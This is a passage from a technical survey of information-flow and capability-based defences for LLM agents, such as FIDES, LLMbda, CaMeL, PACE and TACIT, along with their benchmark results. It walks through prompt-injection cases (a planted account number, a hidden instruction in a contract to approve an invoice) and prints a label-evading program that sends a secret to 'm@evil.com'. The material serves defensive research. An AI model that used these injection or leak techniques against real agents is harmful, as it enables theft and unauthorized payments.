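FIDES guarantees a property called explicit secrecy. Suppose the steps in a run have the combined effect g on stored data. If two stores d₁ and d₂ differ only in secret data, then g(d₁) and g(d₂) must look the same to someone who sees only public data. Because the definition compares the effects of the same steps, it does not cover what an observer learns from which steps the agent took. It therefore leaves out implicit influence, as explicit provenance tracking did in the language that Rajani and colleagues studied. Costa and colleagues chose this limit deliberately, arguing that full noninterference would in practice forbid an agent from writing anything public after it had read anything secret.

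They tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks with planted prompt injections. With policies on, they found no genuine successful attack on any of their agents. The policies sharply reduced completion of banking tasks, many of which require the agent to read a file and act on it. Using GPT-4o, a basic agent completed 98.8 percent of the banking tasks without policies and 37.5 percent with them. FIDES completed 52.5 percent with policies on. Microsoft (2026) has since added FIDES to its Agent Framework as an experimental feature.

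### LLMbda: labels on values and conversations

FIDES's proof covers one agent loop, and CaMeL has no comparable proof. Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language, so that one theorem would cover every agent written in it, including agents that ask a model for code and then run it. They wrote the interpreter and the proofs in Lean, a language whose proofs a computer can check.

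In the basic version, a label is a subset of {U, S}, where U means untrusted and S means secret. The empty set ∅ marks data that is trusted and public. Label l "may flow to" label m, written l ⊑ m, if l is a subset of m. When a program combines values labeled l and m, the result gets their join, l ⊔ m, which is the union of the two labels. For example, {U} ⊔ {S} = {U, S}.

The interpreter also keeps a label, pc, for the program's current position, like the position label in full provenance tracking. If the program branches on a value with label {U}, everything it computes inside the branch gets at least that label.

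The conversation with the model has its own label as well, and a program can change the conversation with these operations:

- `send e` adds the value of e to the conversation and joins its label to the conversation's label.
- `recv` samples a reply from the model. The interpreter reads the reply as code and runs it with the conversation's label as pc, so nothing the code computes can have a lower label.
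- `@e` sends e and then receives the reply.
- `fork e` runs e on a copy of the conversation, keeps the result and restores the original conversation.
- `clear` empties the conversation.

With these operations, a programmer can write the quarantined model as an ordinary function that forks the conversation, clears the copy, sends the untrusted text and returns the reply. The text never enters the main conversation, and the reply keeps the label {U}. CaMeL and FIDES build this separation into the system, whereas in LLMbda the programmer chooses where to use it.

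The last piece is the check `assert l e`, which stops the program unless the label of `e` may flow to `l`. Tool developers put these checks at the start of sensitive tools.

### From an email to a refused payment

The following invented example combines the paper's email agent with its rule for payments. A user asks an agent to pay their landlord $500, using the account number in the latest email. The privileged model writes this plan:

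```
let email = get_last_email state in
let account = quarantine ("Find the account number in: " + email) in
send_money account 500 state
```

An attacker has sent an email that gives the account as `acct_ATTACKER_999`. The interpreter handles the plan as follows:

1. The privileged model has read only the user's request, so the plan starts with pc = ∅.
2. `get_last_email` returns the email's text with label {U}, which the tool's developer assigned.
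3. The program joins the instruction to the text, and the combined prompt gets label ∅ ⊔ {U} = {U}.
4. `quarantine` sends the prompt in a cleared copy of the conversation, whose label rises to {U}. The model replies with `acct_ATTACKER_999`, which also gets {U}. The main conversation still has label ∅.
5. `send_money` begins with a check that the label of `account` may flow to ∅. Since {U} is not a subset of ∅, the interpreter stops the program before it pays anyone.

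The interpreter would also have stopped the program if the email had really come from the landlord. To allow the payment, the plan would have to endorse the account number with `endorse [] account`, where `[]` stands for ∅. The expression returns the same text without the U, and the money then goes to whichever account the quarantined model found.

In the paper's banking agent, the rule for `send_money` checks the integrity of only the recipient. If the user had named the account and left the amount to the email, hidden text could have set the amount. Nikolaou and colleagues give a stricter example rule for the same tool, which rejects an untrusted recipient or amount.

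Endorsement in LLMbda cannot remove S, so endorsing a value labeled {U, S} leaves {S}. It also cannot lower a label below pc. If an attacker gets the agent to run code built from an email, that code runs with pc = {U}, so any endorsement in it has no effect. The attacker gets around this only if the plan has already endorsed the text the code was built from. Garby and colleagues show how a library function could block such chains of endorsements by marking every endorsed value and refusing to endorse it again.

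### Noninterference with random replies

The checks are useful only if the labels are reliable, and the theorem establishes that they are. The theorem is hard to state because a model can answer the same prompt differently each time and a program may never finish.

An observer with label m can see only values whose labels may flow to m. Two programs are indistinguishable to this observer, written e₀ ~ₘ e₁, if they differ only inside values the observer cannot see. The same relation applies to conversations. For integrity questions, m can be {S}, so the observer sees all trusted data and the two starting programs or conversations may differ only in untrusted data, such as the text of an email.

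Let ⟦pc ⊢ C, e⟧ₘ give the probability of each final result, as the observer sees it, when program e starts with conversation C. These probabilities may add up to less than 1, and the remainder is the probability that the program never finishes, including when a failed check stops it.

Two such distributions μ and ν are compatible, written μ ⌣ ν, if some third distribution ω gives every result at least as much probability as each of them does, with a total of at most 1. For programs without endorsement, the theorem is:

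If C₀ ~ₘ C₁ and e₀ ~ₘ e₁, then ⟦pc ⊢ C₀, e₀⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦pc ⊢ C₁, e₁⟧ₘ

It holds for every m and every pc. It means that changing data the observer cannot see changes the visible results only by preventing some runs from finishing.

Suppose an agent given one email always finishes, sending a fixed reminder with probability 0.7 and a fixed apology with probability 0.3. Under the theorem, a different email could stop every run that would have produced the apology, leaving probabilities of 0.7 and 0. It could not raise the reminder's probability to 0.8, because ω would then need a total of at least 0.8 + 0.3 = 1.1.

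The permitted difference is also limited in size. The statistical distance between the two distributions (half the sum of the differences in probability) is at most the average of their chances of not finishing. In the example, the distance is 0.3/2 = 0.15, which equals the limit.

To prove the theorem, Garby and colleagues define a second way of running programs, which skips a computation as soon as its label shows that the observer could not see it. This version finishes at least as often as the real one. It also gives the same distribution for both starting points, because it never uses the data in which they differ, and the proof uses that distribution as ω.

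The guarantee has several limits. An attacker can still stop an agent from working, and can learn something from whether it stopped. The theorem assumes that the model is a fixed source of random replies that depend only on the current conversation, which would not hold for a service that carried memories between conversations. The guarantee also depends on developers labeling data sources correctly and putting checks in the right tools. The theorem covers only what happens inside the program. In the paper's banking agent, the bank account is a record that LLMbda functions update. Garby and colleagues list interaction with real external tools as future work.

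A second theorem covers programs that use endorsement, but only for observers who ignore integrity. The same compatibility holds for these observers, so no endorsement can make a secret leak into public results. The theorem doesn't limit who receives a payment once the plan has endorsed the account number.

### Two gaps in CaMeL's tracking

Garby and colleagues found two places where information gets past CaMeL's labels. In both examples, an attacker wants to learn whether a customer's balance is above some threshold.

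CaMeL blocks the obvious attempt, an `if` statement that tests the balance and sends an email inside the branch. The following version, based on a pattern that researchers have known since the 1970s, gets through:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the program sets `tmp` to False, and CaMeL labels `tmp` as secret. The program then skips the assignment `rich = False`. CaMeL raises a variable's label only when the program assigns to it, so `rich` keeps its public label and the program sends the email. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes False and the program sends nothing. In both cases, `rich` has a public label even though its value reveals whether the balance is above the threshold.

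In LLMbda, the conversation is the only thing a program can overwrite, and the interpreter blocks changes to it when pc may not flow to the conversation's label. A program that branches on a secret cannot add a message to a public conversation, even one labeled secret, because the message's absence when the other branch runs would reveal the secret.

An attacker does not normally write CaMeL's plans, because the privileged model that writes them reads only trusted text. This gap therefore matters mainly if someone misleads that model or the model happens to write such a pattern on its own. Garby and colleagues found a simpler flaw that needs no unusual code. When a CaMeL program inserts an untrusted value into a string literal, CaMeL treats the result as trusted. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) criticizes the choice of Python more generally, because its exceptions, dynamic typing and reflection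 make strong guarantees about information flow difficult.

The other gap is outside the interpreter. When a plan fails, CaMeL uses an ordinary Python loop to prompt the privileged model for a new one, and this loop does not track labels. The loop depends on whether the policy blocked the last attempt, which may depend on a secret. One blocked attempt reveals at most one bit, which the LLMbda theorem also allows, but the loop can repeat the test with a different threshold each time. Ten attempts can distinguish 1,024 possible balances. CaMeL censors the error messages it passes back to the model, but no proof shows that this is enough.

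Randori, the agent that Garby and colleagues wrote in LLMbda, retries only before it reads any real data. The privileged model first tests its plan on invented records, using tools that make no real payments. It then writes a final version, which runs once on the real account. If a label check stops that run, Randori does not try again.

The labels stopped following the information at a skipped assignment in the first gap and at the edge of the interpreter in the second. A guarantee based on labels ends at those points too, even if every check inside the interpreter works correctly.

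### Letting small values through

Some tasks require the planner to use information from untrusted data. For example, a user may ask an agent to create a calendar event if an email contains a meeting request. In FIDES, the planner can query the quarantined model for a yes-or-no answer on whether the email contains one, then inspect that answer.

To permit this, Costa and colleagues add a type to each label and order the types by how much information they can carry:

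bool ⊑ enum["a", "b", "c"] ⊑ string

A policy can then reject an untrusted string but accept an untrusted yes or no. Accepting the yes or no is a form of endorsement, and it is justified because the untrusted source has contributed at most one bit, which is too little to contain an injected instruction. A choice among n options carries at most log₂ n bits.

That protects the planner from a hostile message, but it does not limit the actions that the answer can trigger. Suppose the support agent asks the quarantined model whether a customer's parcel is missing, and refunds $200 if the answer is yes. A customer who lies about the parcel can get the refund just by causing the model to answer yes. The amount and the order number can both be trusted values, as in the attack on the branch, which the capability rules failed to stop.

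Several small answers can also combine to give an email's author control over a larger choice. If a planner asked 14 yes-or-no questions about the email, each splitting the remaining orders in half, the author could pick any one of the 10,000 orders, since 2¹⁴ = 16,384. A policy that judged each answer separately would accept all 14.

Costa and colleagues left this option out of their evaluation because most AgentDojo tasks did not need it, so their results do not show how safe it is. Garby and colleagues object that a reviewer of a run cannot tell an intended exception from a real leak. In LLMbda, the programmer has to write `endorse` where the exception occurs, and a library function can restrict the endorsement to a fixed list of values. The function has to endorse the value before comparing it with the list, because otherwise the branch would depend on untrusted data, pc would rise to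 {U}, and the endorsement would have no effect. Garby and colleagues have not yet proved a limit on how much information this function lets through.

### The AgentDojo banking tests

Garby and colleagues tested Randori on AgentDojo's banking tasks, which combine 16 user requests with nine attacks. They ran each of the 144 pairs three times with each of three models, or 1,296 runs in total, and Randori resisted the attack in all but two. They also ran CaMeL with its policies on and off. Some of those runs did not finish, so for attacks on CaMeL the table counts only completed runs.

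| System | Model | Tasks completed without attacks | Attacks resisted |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 430 of 432 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 36 of 48 | 432 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 432 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 30 of 48 | 432 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 26 of 48 | 432 of 432 |
| CaMeL, policies off | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 239 of 240 |
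| CaMeL, policies off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 378 of 382 |
| CaMeL, policies on | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 231 of 231 |
| CaMeL, policies on | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 357 of 357 |

Randori completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without policies, and nearly twice as many as CaMeL did with them. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) had earlier summarized CaMeL's task performance as comparable to that of other agents. The new tests used only 16 different tasks, so their confidence intervals extend about 20 points or more in each direction, and the tests could miss a sizeable difference.

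Randori's advantage over CaMeL comes partly from a better interpreter and partly from having looser rules for the banking tools and letting its plans endorse data. Without endorsement, Randori could not do the tasks that involved making a payment based on a file, but it still completed more tasks than CaMeL did with policies on.

The security scores are weak evidence of how well the labels work, because CaMeL resisted nearly every attack even with its policies off. In 97 of the 144 pairs, the attack needed a tool call or file that would not appear in a plan for the user's task, so planning before reading was generally enough to defeat it. A benchmark with more attacks that fit the user's plan would test the labels better.

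Both attacks that succeeded against Randori exploited the same user request, which asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described. The attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request, and the interpreter allowed the payment because the plan had endorsed the file's contents. Garby and colleagues consider this outside what information-flow control can prevent, because the user had delegated the decision to the file. Without the endorsement, the interpreter would have blocked the attack along with any legitimate payment request in the file.

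### PACE: checking effects against the user's request

The user's request can help with such cases if it is specific enough. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that combines provenance with a check on what the user authorized. The system is meant for agents whose planning model may already have read hostile text, for example in the description of a tool or a reusable skill, so it does not depend on a plan free of hostile influence. It examines each tool call just before the call runs.

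The system first freezes the call's arguments so that the agent can't change them during the check. It then matches them against a record of earlier values and their origins, and builds a graph of how data could reach the new call's effects. One check looks for a path from untrusted or secret data to an unsafe effect. If there is one, the system computes a minimum-weight cut to break the path, which often means blocking the call.

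The other check compares the call's effects with permissions that PACE derives from the user's authenticated request. Li and colleagues call these permissions capabilities, though they are records that limit an action's purpose, resource, arguments, budget and duration. Text the model writes cannot create or widen these permissions.

Li and colleagues prove their main guarantees for a strict version, PACE-C, in which the call that finally runs must pass both checks. All their experiments used a more permissive version, PACE-P, which may restore a call that the path check blocked if the second check approves it. The restored call can then carry untrusted influence along the path that the path check had cut. They do not claim noninterference for either version.

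They tested PACE-P on eight benchmarks with three models. In 79 comparisons of attack success, it had the lowest rate in 62, tied for the lowest in 14 and did worse than another defence in three. On AgentDojo, with a GPT model, the most effective kind of attack succeeded 100 percent of the time against an undefended agent and 8.11 percent of the time against PACE-P. The share of tasks completed fell only from 73.77 to 72.05 percent. In the same test, attacks succeeded 36.09 percent of the time against CaMeL, which completed 57.02 percent of tasks. CaMeL's attack rate here is far higher than the one Garby and colleagues measured, but the figures are not directly comparable because the two papers used different models, tasks and attacks.

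In a smaller test, a search program attempted 30 goals that the user had not authorized, adapting its attacks to the defence. It reached 21 against an undefended agent and none against PACE-P. With 30 trials, the true success rate against PACE-P could still be as high as about 11 percent.

An experiment on 1,167 cases measured the two checks separately. In the AgentDojo cases, either check alone reduced attack success from 37.4 percent to zero. The path check, which tracks influence, also cut the share of completed tasks from 76.8 to 13.6 percent, while the authorization check, which compares effects with the request, left it at 64.6 percent. In the experiment's cases from AgentDyn, another benchmark, the full system cut the share of completed tasks from 66.7 to 33.3 percent, although on the complete benchmark the drop was below three percentage points.

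A support agent would be harder to protect this way, because the only person who asks for a particular refund is the customer, who may be lying. The company's standing instruction to handle refund requests is authenticated, but it doesn't determine which customers deserve a refund. PACE's guarantees also cover only the effects declared in a tool's description. If the description of the queue tool lists only "append a record", Li and colleagues' second check can approve the record without checking the refund. Someone would have to read the dispatcher's code to declare the refund as an effect, then update the description whenever that code changed.

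## Type systems that check capabilities before agent code runs

An interpreter that checks labels during a run may stop a program after it has already sent an email or changed a file. A compiler can check the whole program and reject it before any of it runs. Odersky and colleagues used this approach in TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types). The agent acts by writing short programs in Scala, a general-purpose language, and the compiler rejects any program that uses a capability its types do not declare.

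TACIT runs as a server that existing agents can use without modification. The agent sends the server a program, and the server compiles it with a library that provides access to files, commands and the network. If the compiler finds an error, the agent receives the error message and can try again. An agent with other tools could avoid the compiler, so lampepfl's *TACIT*, the guide that accompanies the code, advises users to switch off the agent's built-in file, shell and web tools.

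### Capture sets and pure functions

A type usually describes what kind of value an expression produces, such as a string or a list of numbers. Scala's experimental capture checking adds a capture set to the type, which lists the capabilities that the value may use. For example, a logger of type `Logger^{out}` may use only the capability `out`. The idea comes from a formal language, described by Boruch-Gruszecki and Odersky, in which types record the variables that a value captures.

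Functions have capture sets too. Suppose `f` is a capability to write to one file. The function `(s: String) => f.write(s)` takes a string and writes it there, so the compiler gives it this type:

`String ->{f} Unit`

A function of type `String -> Unit` takes a string and returns no useful result. Because no capabilities are listed after the arrow, its capture set is empty and it is called pure. It can compute with its argument, but it holds no capability to write a file or contact a server.

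A value's capture set must include every capability the value uses and may include others, so it is an upper bound, like the safe bounds on authority. The compiler accepts a pure function wherever a function using `f` is allowed, but it rejects a function using `f` where a pure function is required.

Tracking also allows TACIT to relax the object-capability model's rule against global objects that give access to resources. The model forbids these objects because any code could use them. In Scala, a function's capture set includes any such object it uses, so code that requires a pure function still cannot receive that function.

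### Classified data and capabilities that expire

TACIT protects secrets by allowing only pure functions to process them. The operator marks directories as classified. When a program reads a file from one of them, it gets the text inside a wrapper of type `Classified[String]`. The wrapper's `map` method applies a function to the text and puts the result in a new wrapper, but it accepts only pure functions. If the program prints a wrapped value, the user's terminal shows the contents, while the agent sees only `Classified(****)`.

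For jobs that need a language model, such as summarizing a contract, the library's `chat` function sends the wrapped text to a second model, which the operator trusts, and wraps the reply. The agent's own model, usually a cloud service, never receives the text.

Code gets access to files by calling `requestFileSystem`, which takes a directory and a block of code. It creates a capability for that directory, which the code can use only inside the block. The compiler rejects a block that returns anything still holding the capability, such as a function that would read a file later, because the returned value's type would have to name a capability that does not exist outside the block. The library checks at run time that each path lies within the directory, since a program may compute the path while it runs.

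The compiler accepts this program, adapted from the TACIT guide:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val contract = readClassified("secrets/contract.txt")
  val summary = chat("Summarize this contract:", contract)
  writeClassified("secrets/summary.txt", summary)
}
```

The contract and the summary stay in wrappers throughout, and the summary goes into another classified file. The next program tries to copy the contract into an ordinary file, where the agent could read it:

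```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val contract = readClassified("secrets/contract.txt")
  contract.map { text => access("notes.txt").write(text) }
}
```

The function in the third line uses the file-system capability to open `notes.txt`, so it is not pure and `map` cannot accept it. The compiler reports a type mismatch, and the server runs none of the program, including the line that reads the contract.

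### Three properties and the rules of safe mode

Odersky and colleagues require three properties of the language in which an agent writes:

- Capability safety: programs cannot forge capabilities or make the compiler forget that a value uses one.
- Capability completeness: capabilities regulate every effect that matters for safety, except those that the system can contain at run time.
- Local purity: the language can express that a particular computation uses only certain capabilities, or none.

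The wrapper needs all three. If a program could forge capabilities, it could forge the one that opens the wrapper. If code could use the network without a capability, a supposedly pure function could leak the secret. Without local purity, `map` could not require a pure function.

Ordinary Scala does not have these properties, because a type cast, for example, can make the compiler treat a function that writes files as a pure one. Safe mode, which Mazur, in *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!*, describes as a new experimental subset of the language, has these rules:

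1. No unchecked type casts or pattern matches.
2. No features from `caps.unsafe`, the module of deliberate exceptions to capture checking.
3. No `@unchecked` annotations, which turn off compiler checks.
4. No reflection, through which a program can look up and call code by name as it runs.
5. Capture checking must be on, and the compiler must also track changes to variables. TACIT adds a check for missing values.
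6. Agent code may use global objects and functions only if they are safe themselves.

An early version of TACIT only approximated these rules. According to lampepfl, it used a validator that searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns. As with the filters in Semantic Kernel, any dangerous construct missing from the list would get past such a search.

Safe mode allows exceptions, the errors that interrupt a program, even though a program can leak information by failing at a chosen moment. According to Scala's *Safe Mode* reference page, tracking every possible division by zero or memory shortage would be too cumbersome. TACIT instead catches exceptions at run time and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap. TACIT does not cover timing, so a function inside `map` could leak one bit about a secret by running for a long or a short time.

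### The trusted base and code declared safe

The trusted base consists of the Scala compiler, the capability library, the runtime that executes accepted programs and, if the operator uses one, the local model that reads classified text. The cloud model, all the code it writes and everything the agent reads are untrusted. Odersky and colleagues assume that the cloud model may cooperate fully with an attacker.

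Computer-checked proofs exist for the basic type system behind capture checking, but a further proof would be needed to show that safe mode provides capability safety and local purity. Type checking also cannot establish that the service behind `chat` discards the text it receives, so the operator has to ensure that.

The library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and parts of it must break the rules of safe mode, since a program written entirely in safe mode could not print its result. A programmer marks such code `@assumeSafe`, which lets agent programs call it, but the compiler does not check that the code is safe. In one of Scala's examples, a cache stores earlier results in a variable that capture checking ignores. This is harmless only if every cached result comes from a pure function, which the programmer must verify by hand or with a separate proof.

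Another example is a mail module, `CheckedMailer`, which shows the user each message and sends it only after the user agrees. Mazur's announcement has a module of the same name with no confirmation step. Both compile, because the compiler accepts the annotation whether or not the module asks the user before sending. An agent cannot add the annotation to its own code, so safety depends on the people who write and review the library.

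VirtusLab's *Safe Scala* illustrates the same division of work with a network library that could limit agent code to domains on an approved list. The compiler ensures that the agent goes through the library, but the library checks the domain against the list at run time. A mistake in that check would affect every program the compiler accepted.

### Tests of leaks and completed tasks

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a directory of secrets, including API keys and confidential documents. Each model attempted 12 ordinary tasks, such as anonymizing employee reviews, once with each of 10 injected attacks. In another 11 trials, the user asked for the secrets, either directly or under a pretext such as an emergency password change. The models did all 131 trials twice, first with the secrets in wrappers and then with them as plain strings. The researchers counted a leak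 if any secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Secrets | Injection trials without a leak | Requests for secrets without a leak | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Wrapped | 120 of 120 | 11 of 11 | 99.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Plain | 120 of 120 | 9 of 11 | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Wrapped | 120 of 120 | 11 of 11 | 90.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Plain | 117 of 120 | 3 of 11 | 88.3% |

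The wrapper reduced leaks from 13 to zero. Only three of the 13 came from injected text, so the test is better evidence about users who ask for secrets than about prompt injection. Claude's low score with plain strings may be an artifact of the test, because Claude often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

If the compiler and library are correct, the result should be the same for any model, so the trials mostly test the implementation. A determined search for bugs would test it harder. Biały and Warchoł (2026), in *Making the AI agents safe with Scala*, mention capture-the-flag projects that used frontier AI models to find exploits against TACIT. Their abstract is for a talk about CapybaraClaw, an agent based on TACIT and meant to run permanently.

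A separate experiment tested whether writing typed programs makes agents less competent. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, three models used either TACIT or ordinary tool calls for airline and retail tasks. TACIT scored higher in all six comparisons, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax M2.5 resolved 125 with TACIT and 130 without it. The customer-service tools returned ordinary values rather than wrapped ones, so that part of the experiment measured the effect of typed programming but not of hiding data from the agent.

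The AgentDojo tests come closer to measuring that second drawback, because most of their methods that read emails, files or messages return wrapped values. In *LACUNA*, Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026) later ran the same tests on a related system of the same name. It lets a running Scala program ask a model to write the program's next piece, and the compiler checks each piece against the surrounding code. The table gives the share of user tasks completed and the number of successful attacks. The figures for CaMeL come from its developers.

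| Model | System | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 of 963 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 of 963 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 of 949 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 of 963 |
| o4-mini-high | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 of 963 |
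| o4-mini-high | LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 of 949 |

Odersky and colleagues call TACIT's task completion comparable to CaMeL's. That is roughly true with Gemini, except on travel tasks, where CaMeL failed almost completely. With o4-mini-high, however, CaMeL led by 29 points on workspace tasks and 21 on Slack tasks. The one attack counted against TACIT was a hotel review that recommended a rival hotel. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the review to the user, which the policy allowed.

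Zhao and colleagues found a larger drop in performance on τ²-bench. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA solved 76.0 percent of 392 tasks, while an agent using ordinary tool calls solved 90.0 percent. A weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, wrote such poor Scala for telecom tasks that the compiler rejected 89 percent of its programs. The rejected programs did no harm, but the agent made no progress on most turns of the conversations.

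### A permitted write with a privileged reader

The accepted program above writes a summary of a contract to a file. Suppose a payment program reads that file every night and pays any invoice that the summary lists as approved. The other party hides an instruction in the contract to list invoice 77 as approved. The local model follows the instruction, and the payment program pays the invoice that night.

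TACIT worked as designed, but whoever wrote the contract still got a deputy to spend money they had no right to spend. The agent's program forged no capability, and it had the right to write to the summary file. Inside the program, the contract's text never left its wrapper. The capture set covers access to files but not payments, because the agent's program never calls the payment program.

The types control where the program may send data, but not what the data leads its recipients to do. The trusted model can be fooled as easily as the cloud model. It has no tools, so its mistakes can only appear as text, but here text is enough to cause harm. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that LACUNA has this limit, writing that an attacker who gets the model to misuse a capability the task legitimately requires "is not blocked". They propose more exact types as future work, such as one that accepts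 only integers within a certain range. Such a type could prevent the agent from writing an amount above $200, but the payment program would still determine how often it pays that amount.

In VirtusLab's demonstration, a safe program writes the number 55 to `result.txt`, and the agent has no function for reading it back. Any other program with access to the file can still act on that number, so denying the agent read access would not prevent this.

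TACIT has the same problem with commands that an agent is allowed to run. Odersky and colleagues warn that such commands run outside safe mode and recommend allowing only a short list of safe ones, such as `git diff` and `sbt`. But `sbt`, Scala's build tool, runs code from the project's own build files, so an agent allowed to edit those files and run `sbt` can run code that the compiler has never checked in safe mode. Each permission is reasonable alone and appears in the agent's types, but their combined effect depends on how `sbt` behaves. For critical systems, the researchers recommend adding a sandbox.

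### Static checks and run-time labels compared

Static checking adds little to the running time. The compiler takes less than a second for a typical program, and most of the added time comes from calling the model again when the compiler rejects one. On τ²-bench, the compiler rejected between 0.3 and 7.9 percent of programs, depending on the model and domain. Developers must also describe their tools in Scala, which took a few hundred lines for each of the two customer-service domains. Run-time labels require a special interpreter, and the one in CaMeL does not let the agent define its own functions.

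Capture checking can also catch leaks that CaMeL's labels miss, because it covers every path through a program, including those that a particular run does not take. The program that got a customer's balance past CaMeL's labels relied on skipping an assignment. In TACIT, a program can branch on a wrapped balance only inside a function passed to `map`, and that function cannot change variables outside it, so the compiler would reject the program whatever the balance was.

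Labels can express more detailed policies. An interpreter can compare a document's list of permitted readers with an email's recipient, even if the program only works out the recipient during the run. `Classified` makes no such distinctions and does not record which source a value came from, although a library designer can build some of this into the types. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) does so for an agent that writes bibliographies. Its Haskell library can add an entry to the output file only if the entry has a special type, and only a function that fetches records from the DBLP database can create values of that type. In 100 tasks, the agent produced no false citations among 925, compared with 19 among 1,002 for an ordinary agent.

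Odersky and colleagues argue that run-time systems lose a value's labels once it enters the model's conversation as ordinary text, and that TACIT avoids this by never showing the model classified text. However, the run-time systems FIDES and LLMbda label the conversation itself, so the objection does not apply to them.

TACIT relies on a full production compiler and on every module marked `@assumeSafe`. LLMbda relies on a much smaller interpreter with a computer-checked proof, and on the labels and checks that developers choose. Forgetting to classify a directory in TACIT is much the same mistake as labeling a source as public in LLMbda.

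Garby and colleagues conjecture that static checks before a program runs complement labels, which handle whatever depends on the run. Zhou and colleagues have built a system of this kind, ELBA, in which Haskell's types force agent code to use LIO, an established library that tracks labels at run time. When a program reads a web page, for instance, LIO lowers the trust level of the whole computation, and later attempts to write somewhere more trusted fail.

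Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL on AgentDojo's Slack tasks, using four models. With policies on, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of the 21 tasks and CaMeL 4 to 6, though ELBA took about three times as long because it called the model more often. Both systems resisted every standard attack even with policies off, so those attacks could not show whether the policies worked. The researchers therefore simulated the worst case by making the part of the agent that read an injection follow the injected instructions. ELBA then resisted 425 to 621 of 735 attacks with policies off, depending on the model, and all 735 for every model with policies on. Turning policies on also reduced the number of tasks it completed from 494–558 to 294–351.

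AgentDojo's tools are written in Python, so ELBA had to call them by exchanging messages with another process, where Haskell's types and LIO's labels do not apply.

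## Passing capabilities from one process to another

ELBA lost the protection of its types when it called tools in another process, and capabilities have the same problem. Inside one program, the language runtime keeps references separate from ordinary data, so code cannot forge a reference. Two processes exchange only bytes, so if the sender wrote a reference as a number, any program that learned or guessed the number could send the same bytes and use the object it refers to.

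In the capability version of the support example, a mail program gives the agent's harness a capability to request a refund only on the sender's order. The harness and the dispatcher are separate programs, so this design works only if the capability can be passed between them in a message or a queue record.

### Open files sent through the kernel

Unix keeps a table of open files for each process, and a file descriptor is only a position in that table. The online guide *sockets 101* demonstrates this with two command shells. Descriptor 5 refers to the file `/etc/hosts` in one shell but usually doesn't exist in the other. Sending another process the text "5" therefore doesn't give it access to the file.

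To share the open file itself, the process must ask the kernel. Arch Linux's *UNIX(7)*, a manual page, describes how this works over Unix sockets, which connect processes on the same machine:

1. The sender attaches the descriptor to a message as "ancillary data", separate from the message's ordinary bytes.
2. The kernel looks up the descriptor in the sender's table and refuses to send the message if it finds no open file there.
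3. When the receiver accepts the message, the kernel adds an entry for the same open file to the receiver's table, usually under a different number.

A sender can pass on only files it has open, and another process that copies the message's ordinary bytes gains no access. The same sockets can also carry the sender's user ID, which the kernel checks. But a receiver that used the ID to decide which files to open would again be relying on an access-control list.

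Unix treats a connection as an open file too. The mail program could therefore open a connection to the dispatcher for order 1001 and pass it to the harness. The harness would send only a route, such as `refund`, and the dispatcher would apply it to order 1001. This works only while all three programs are running on one machine. A queue stored in a database cannot hold an open connection.

### References across a network

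Machines on a network don't share a kernel, so they have to use cryptography to pass capabilities. OCapN (Object Capability Network) is a set of draft specifications for references between machines. In *Introducing OCapN, interoperable capabilities over the network*, Tallon credits part of the design to earlier systems, including the programming language E. Miller, whose thesis describes E, pictures such systems as "object-capability islands" that exchange messages over a "cryptographic capability sea".

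When two machines open a secure connection, each keeps a numbered table of the objects it has shared with the other. *explain captp*, a set of design notes for CapTP, includes a message that sends the request `read-balance` to the object at position 3. That number is meaningful only on this connection, so a program elsewhere can't use it. The machine at the other end can try any number but can reach only objects it already has access to.

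Sharing a reference is harder when it involves three machines. Suppose Alice, an object on machine A, wants to give Bob, on machine B, a reference to Carol, on machine C. Carol's position in the table for A's connection means nothing to B. The design notes outline this procedure:

1. A tells C that it is leaving a gift, numbered 25, and that the gift is Carol.
2. A gives B a signed certificate with B's public key, C's network address, an identifier for A's connection to C, and the gift's number.
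3. B puts the certificate inside a message that it signs with its own key, and sends the message to C.
4. C checks both signatures and gives B its own reference to Carol.

Someone who copies the certificate can't redeem it without B's private key. *3-vat/machine handoffs, certificates only, no handoff tables required*, a mailing-list proposal, omits the gift, and the certificate instead contains Carol's position in A's table. The drawback is that B can then guess roughly how long A and C have been connected.

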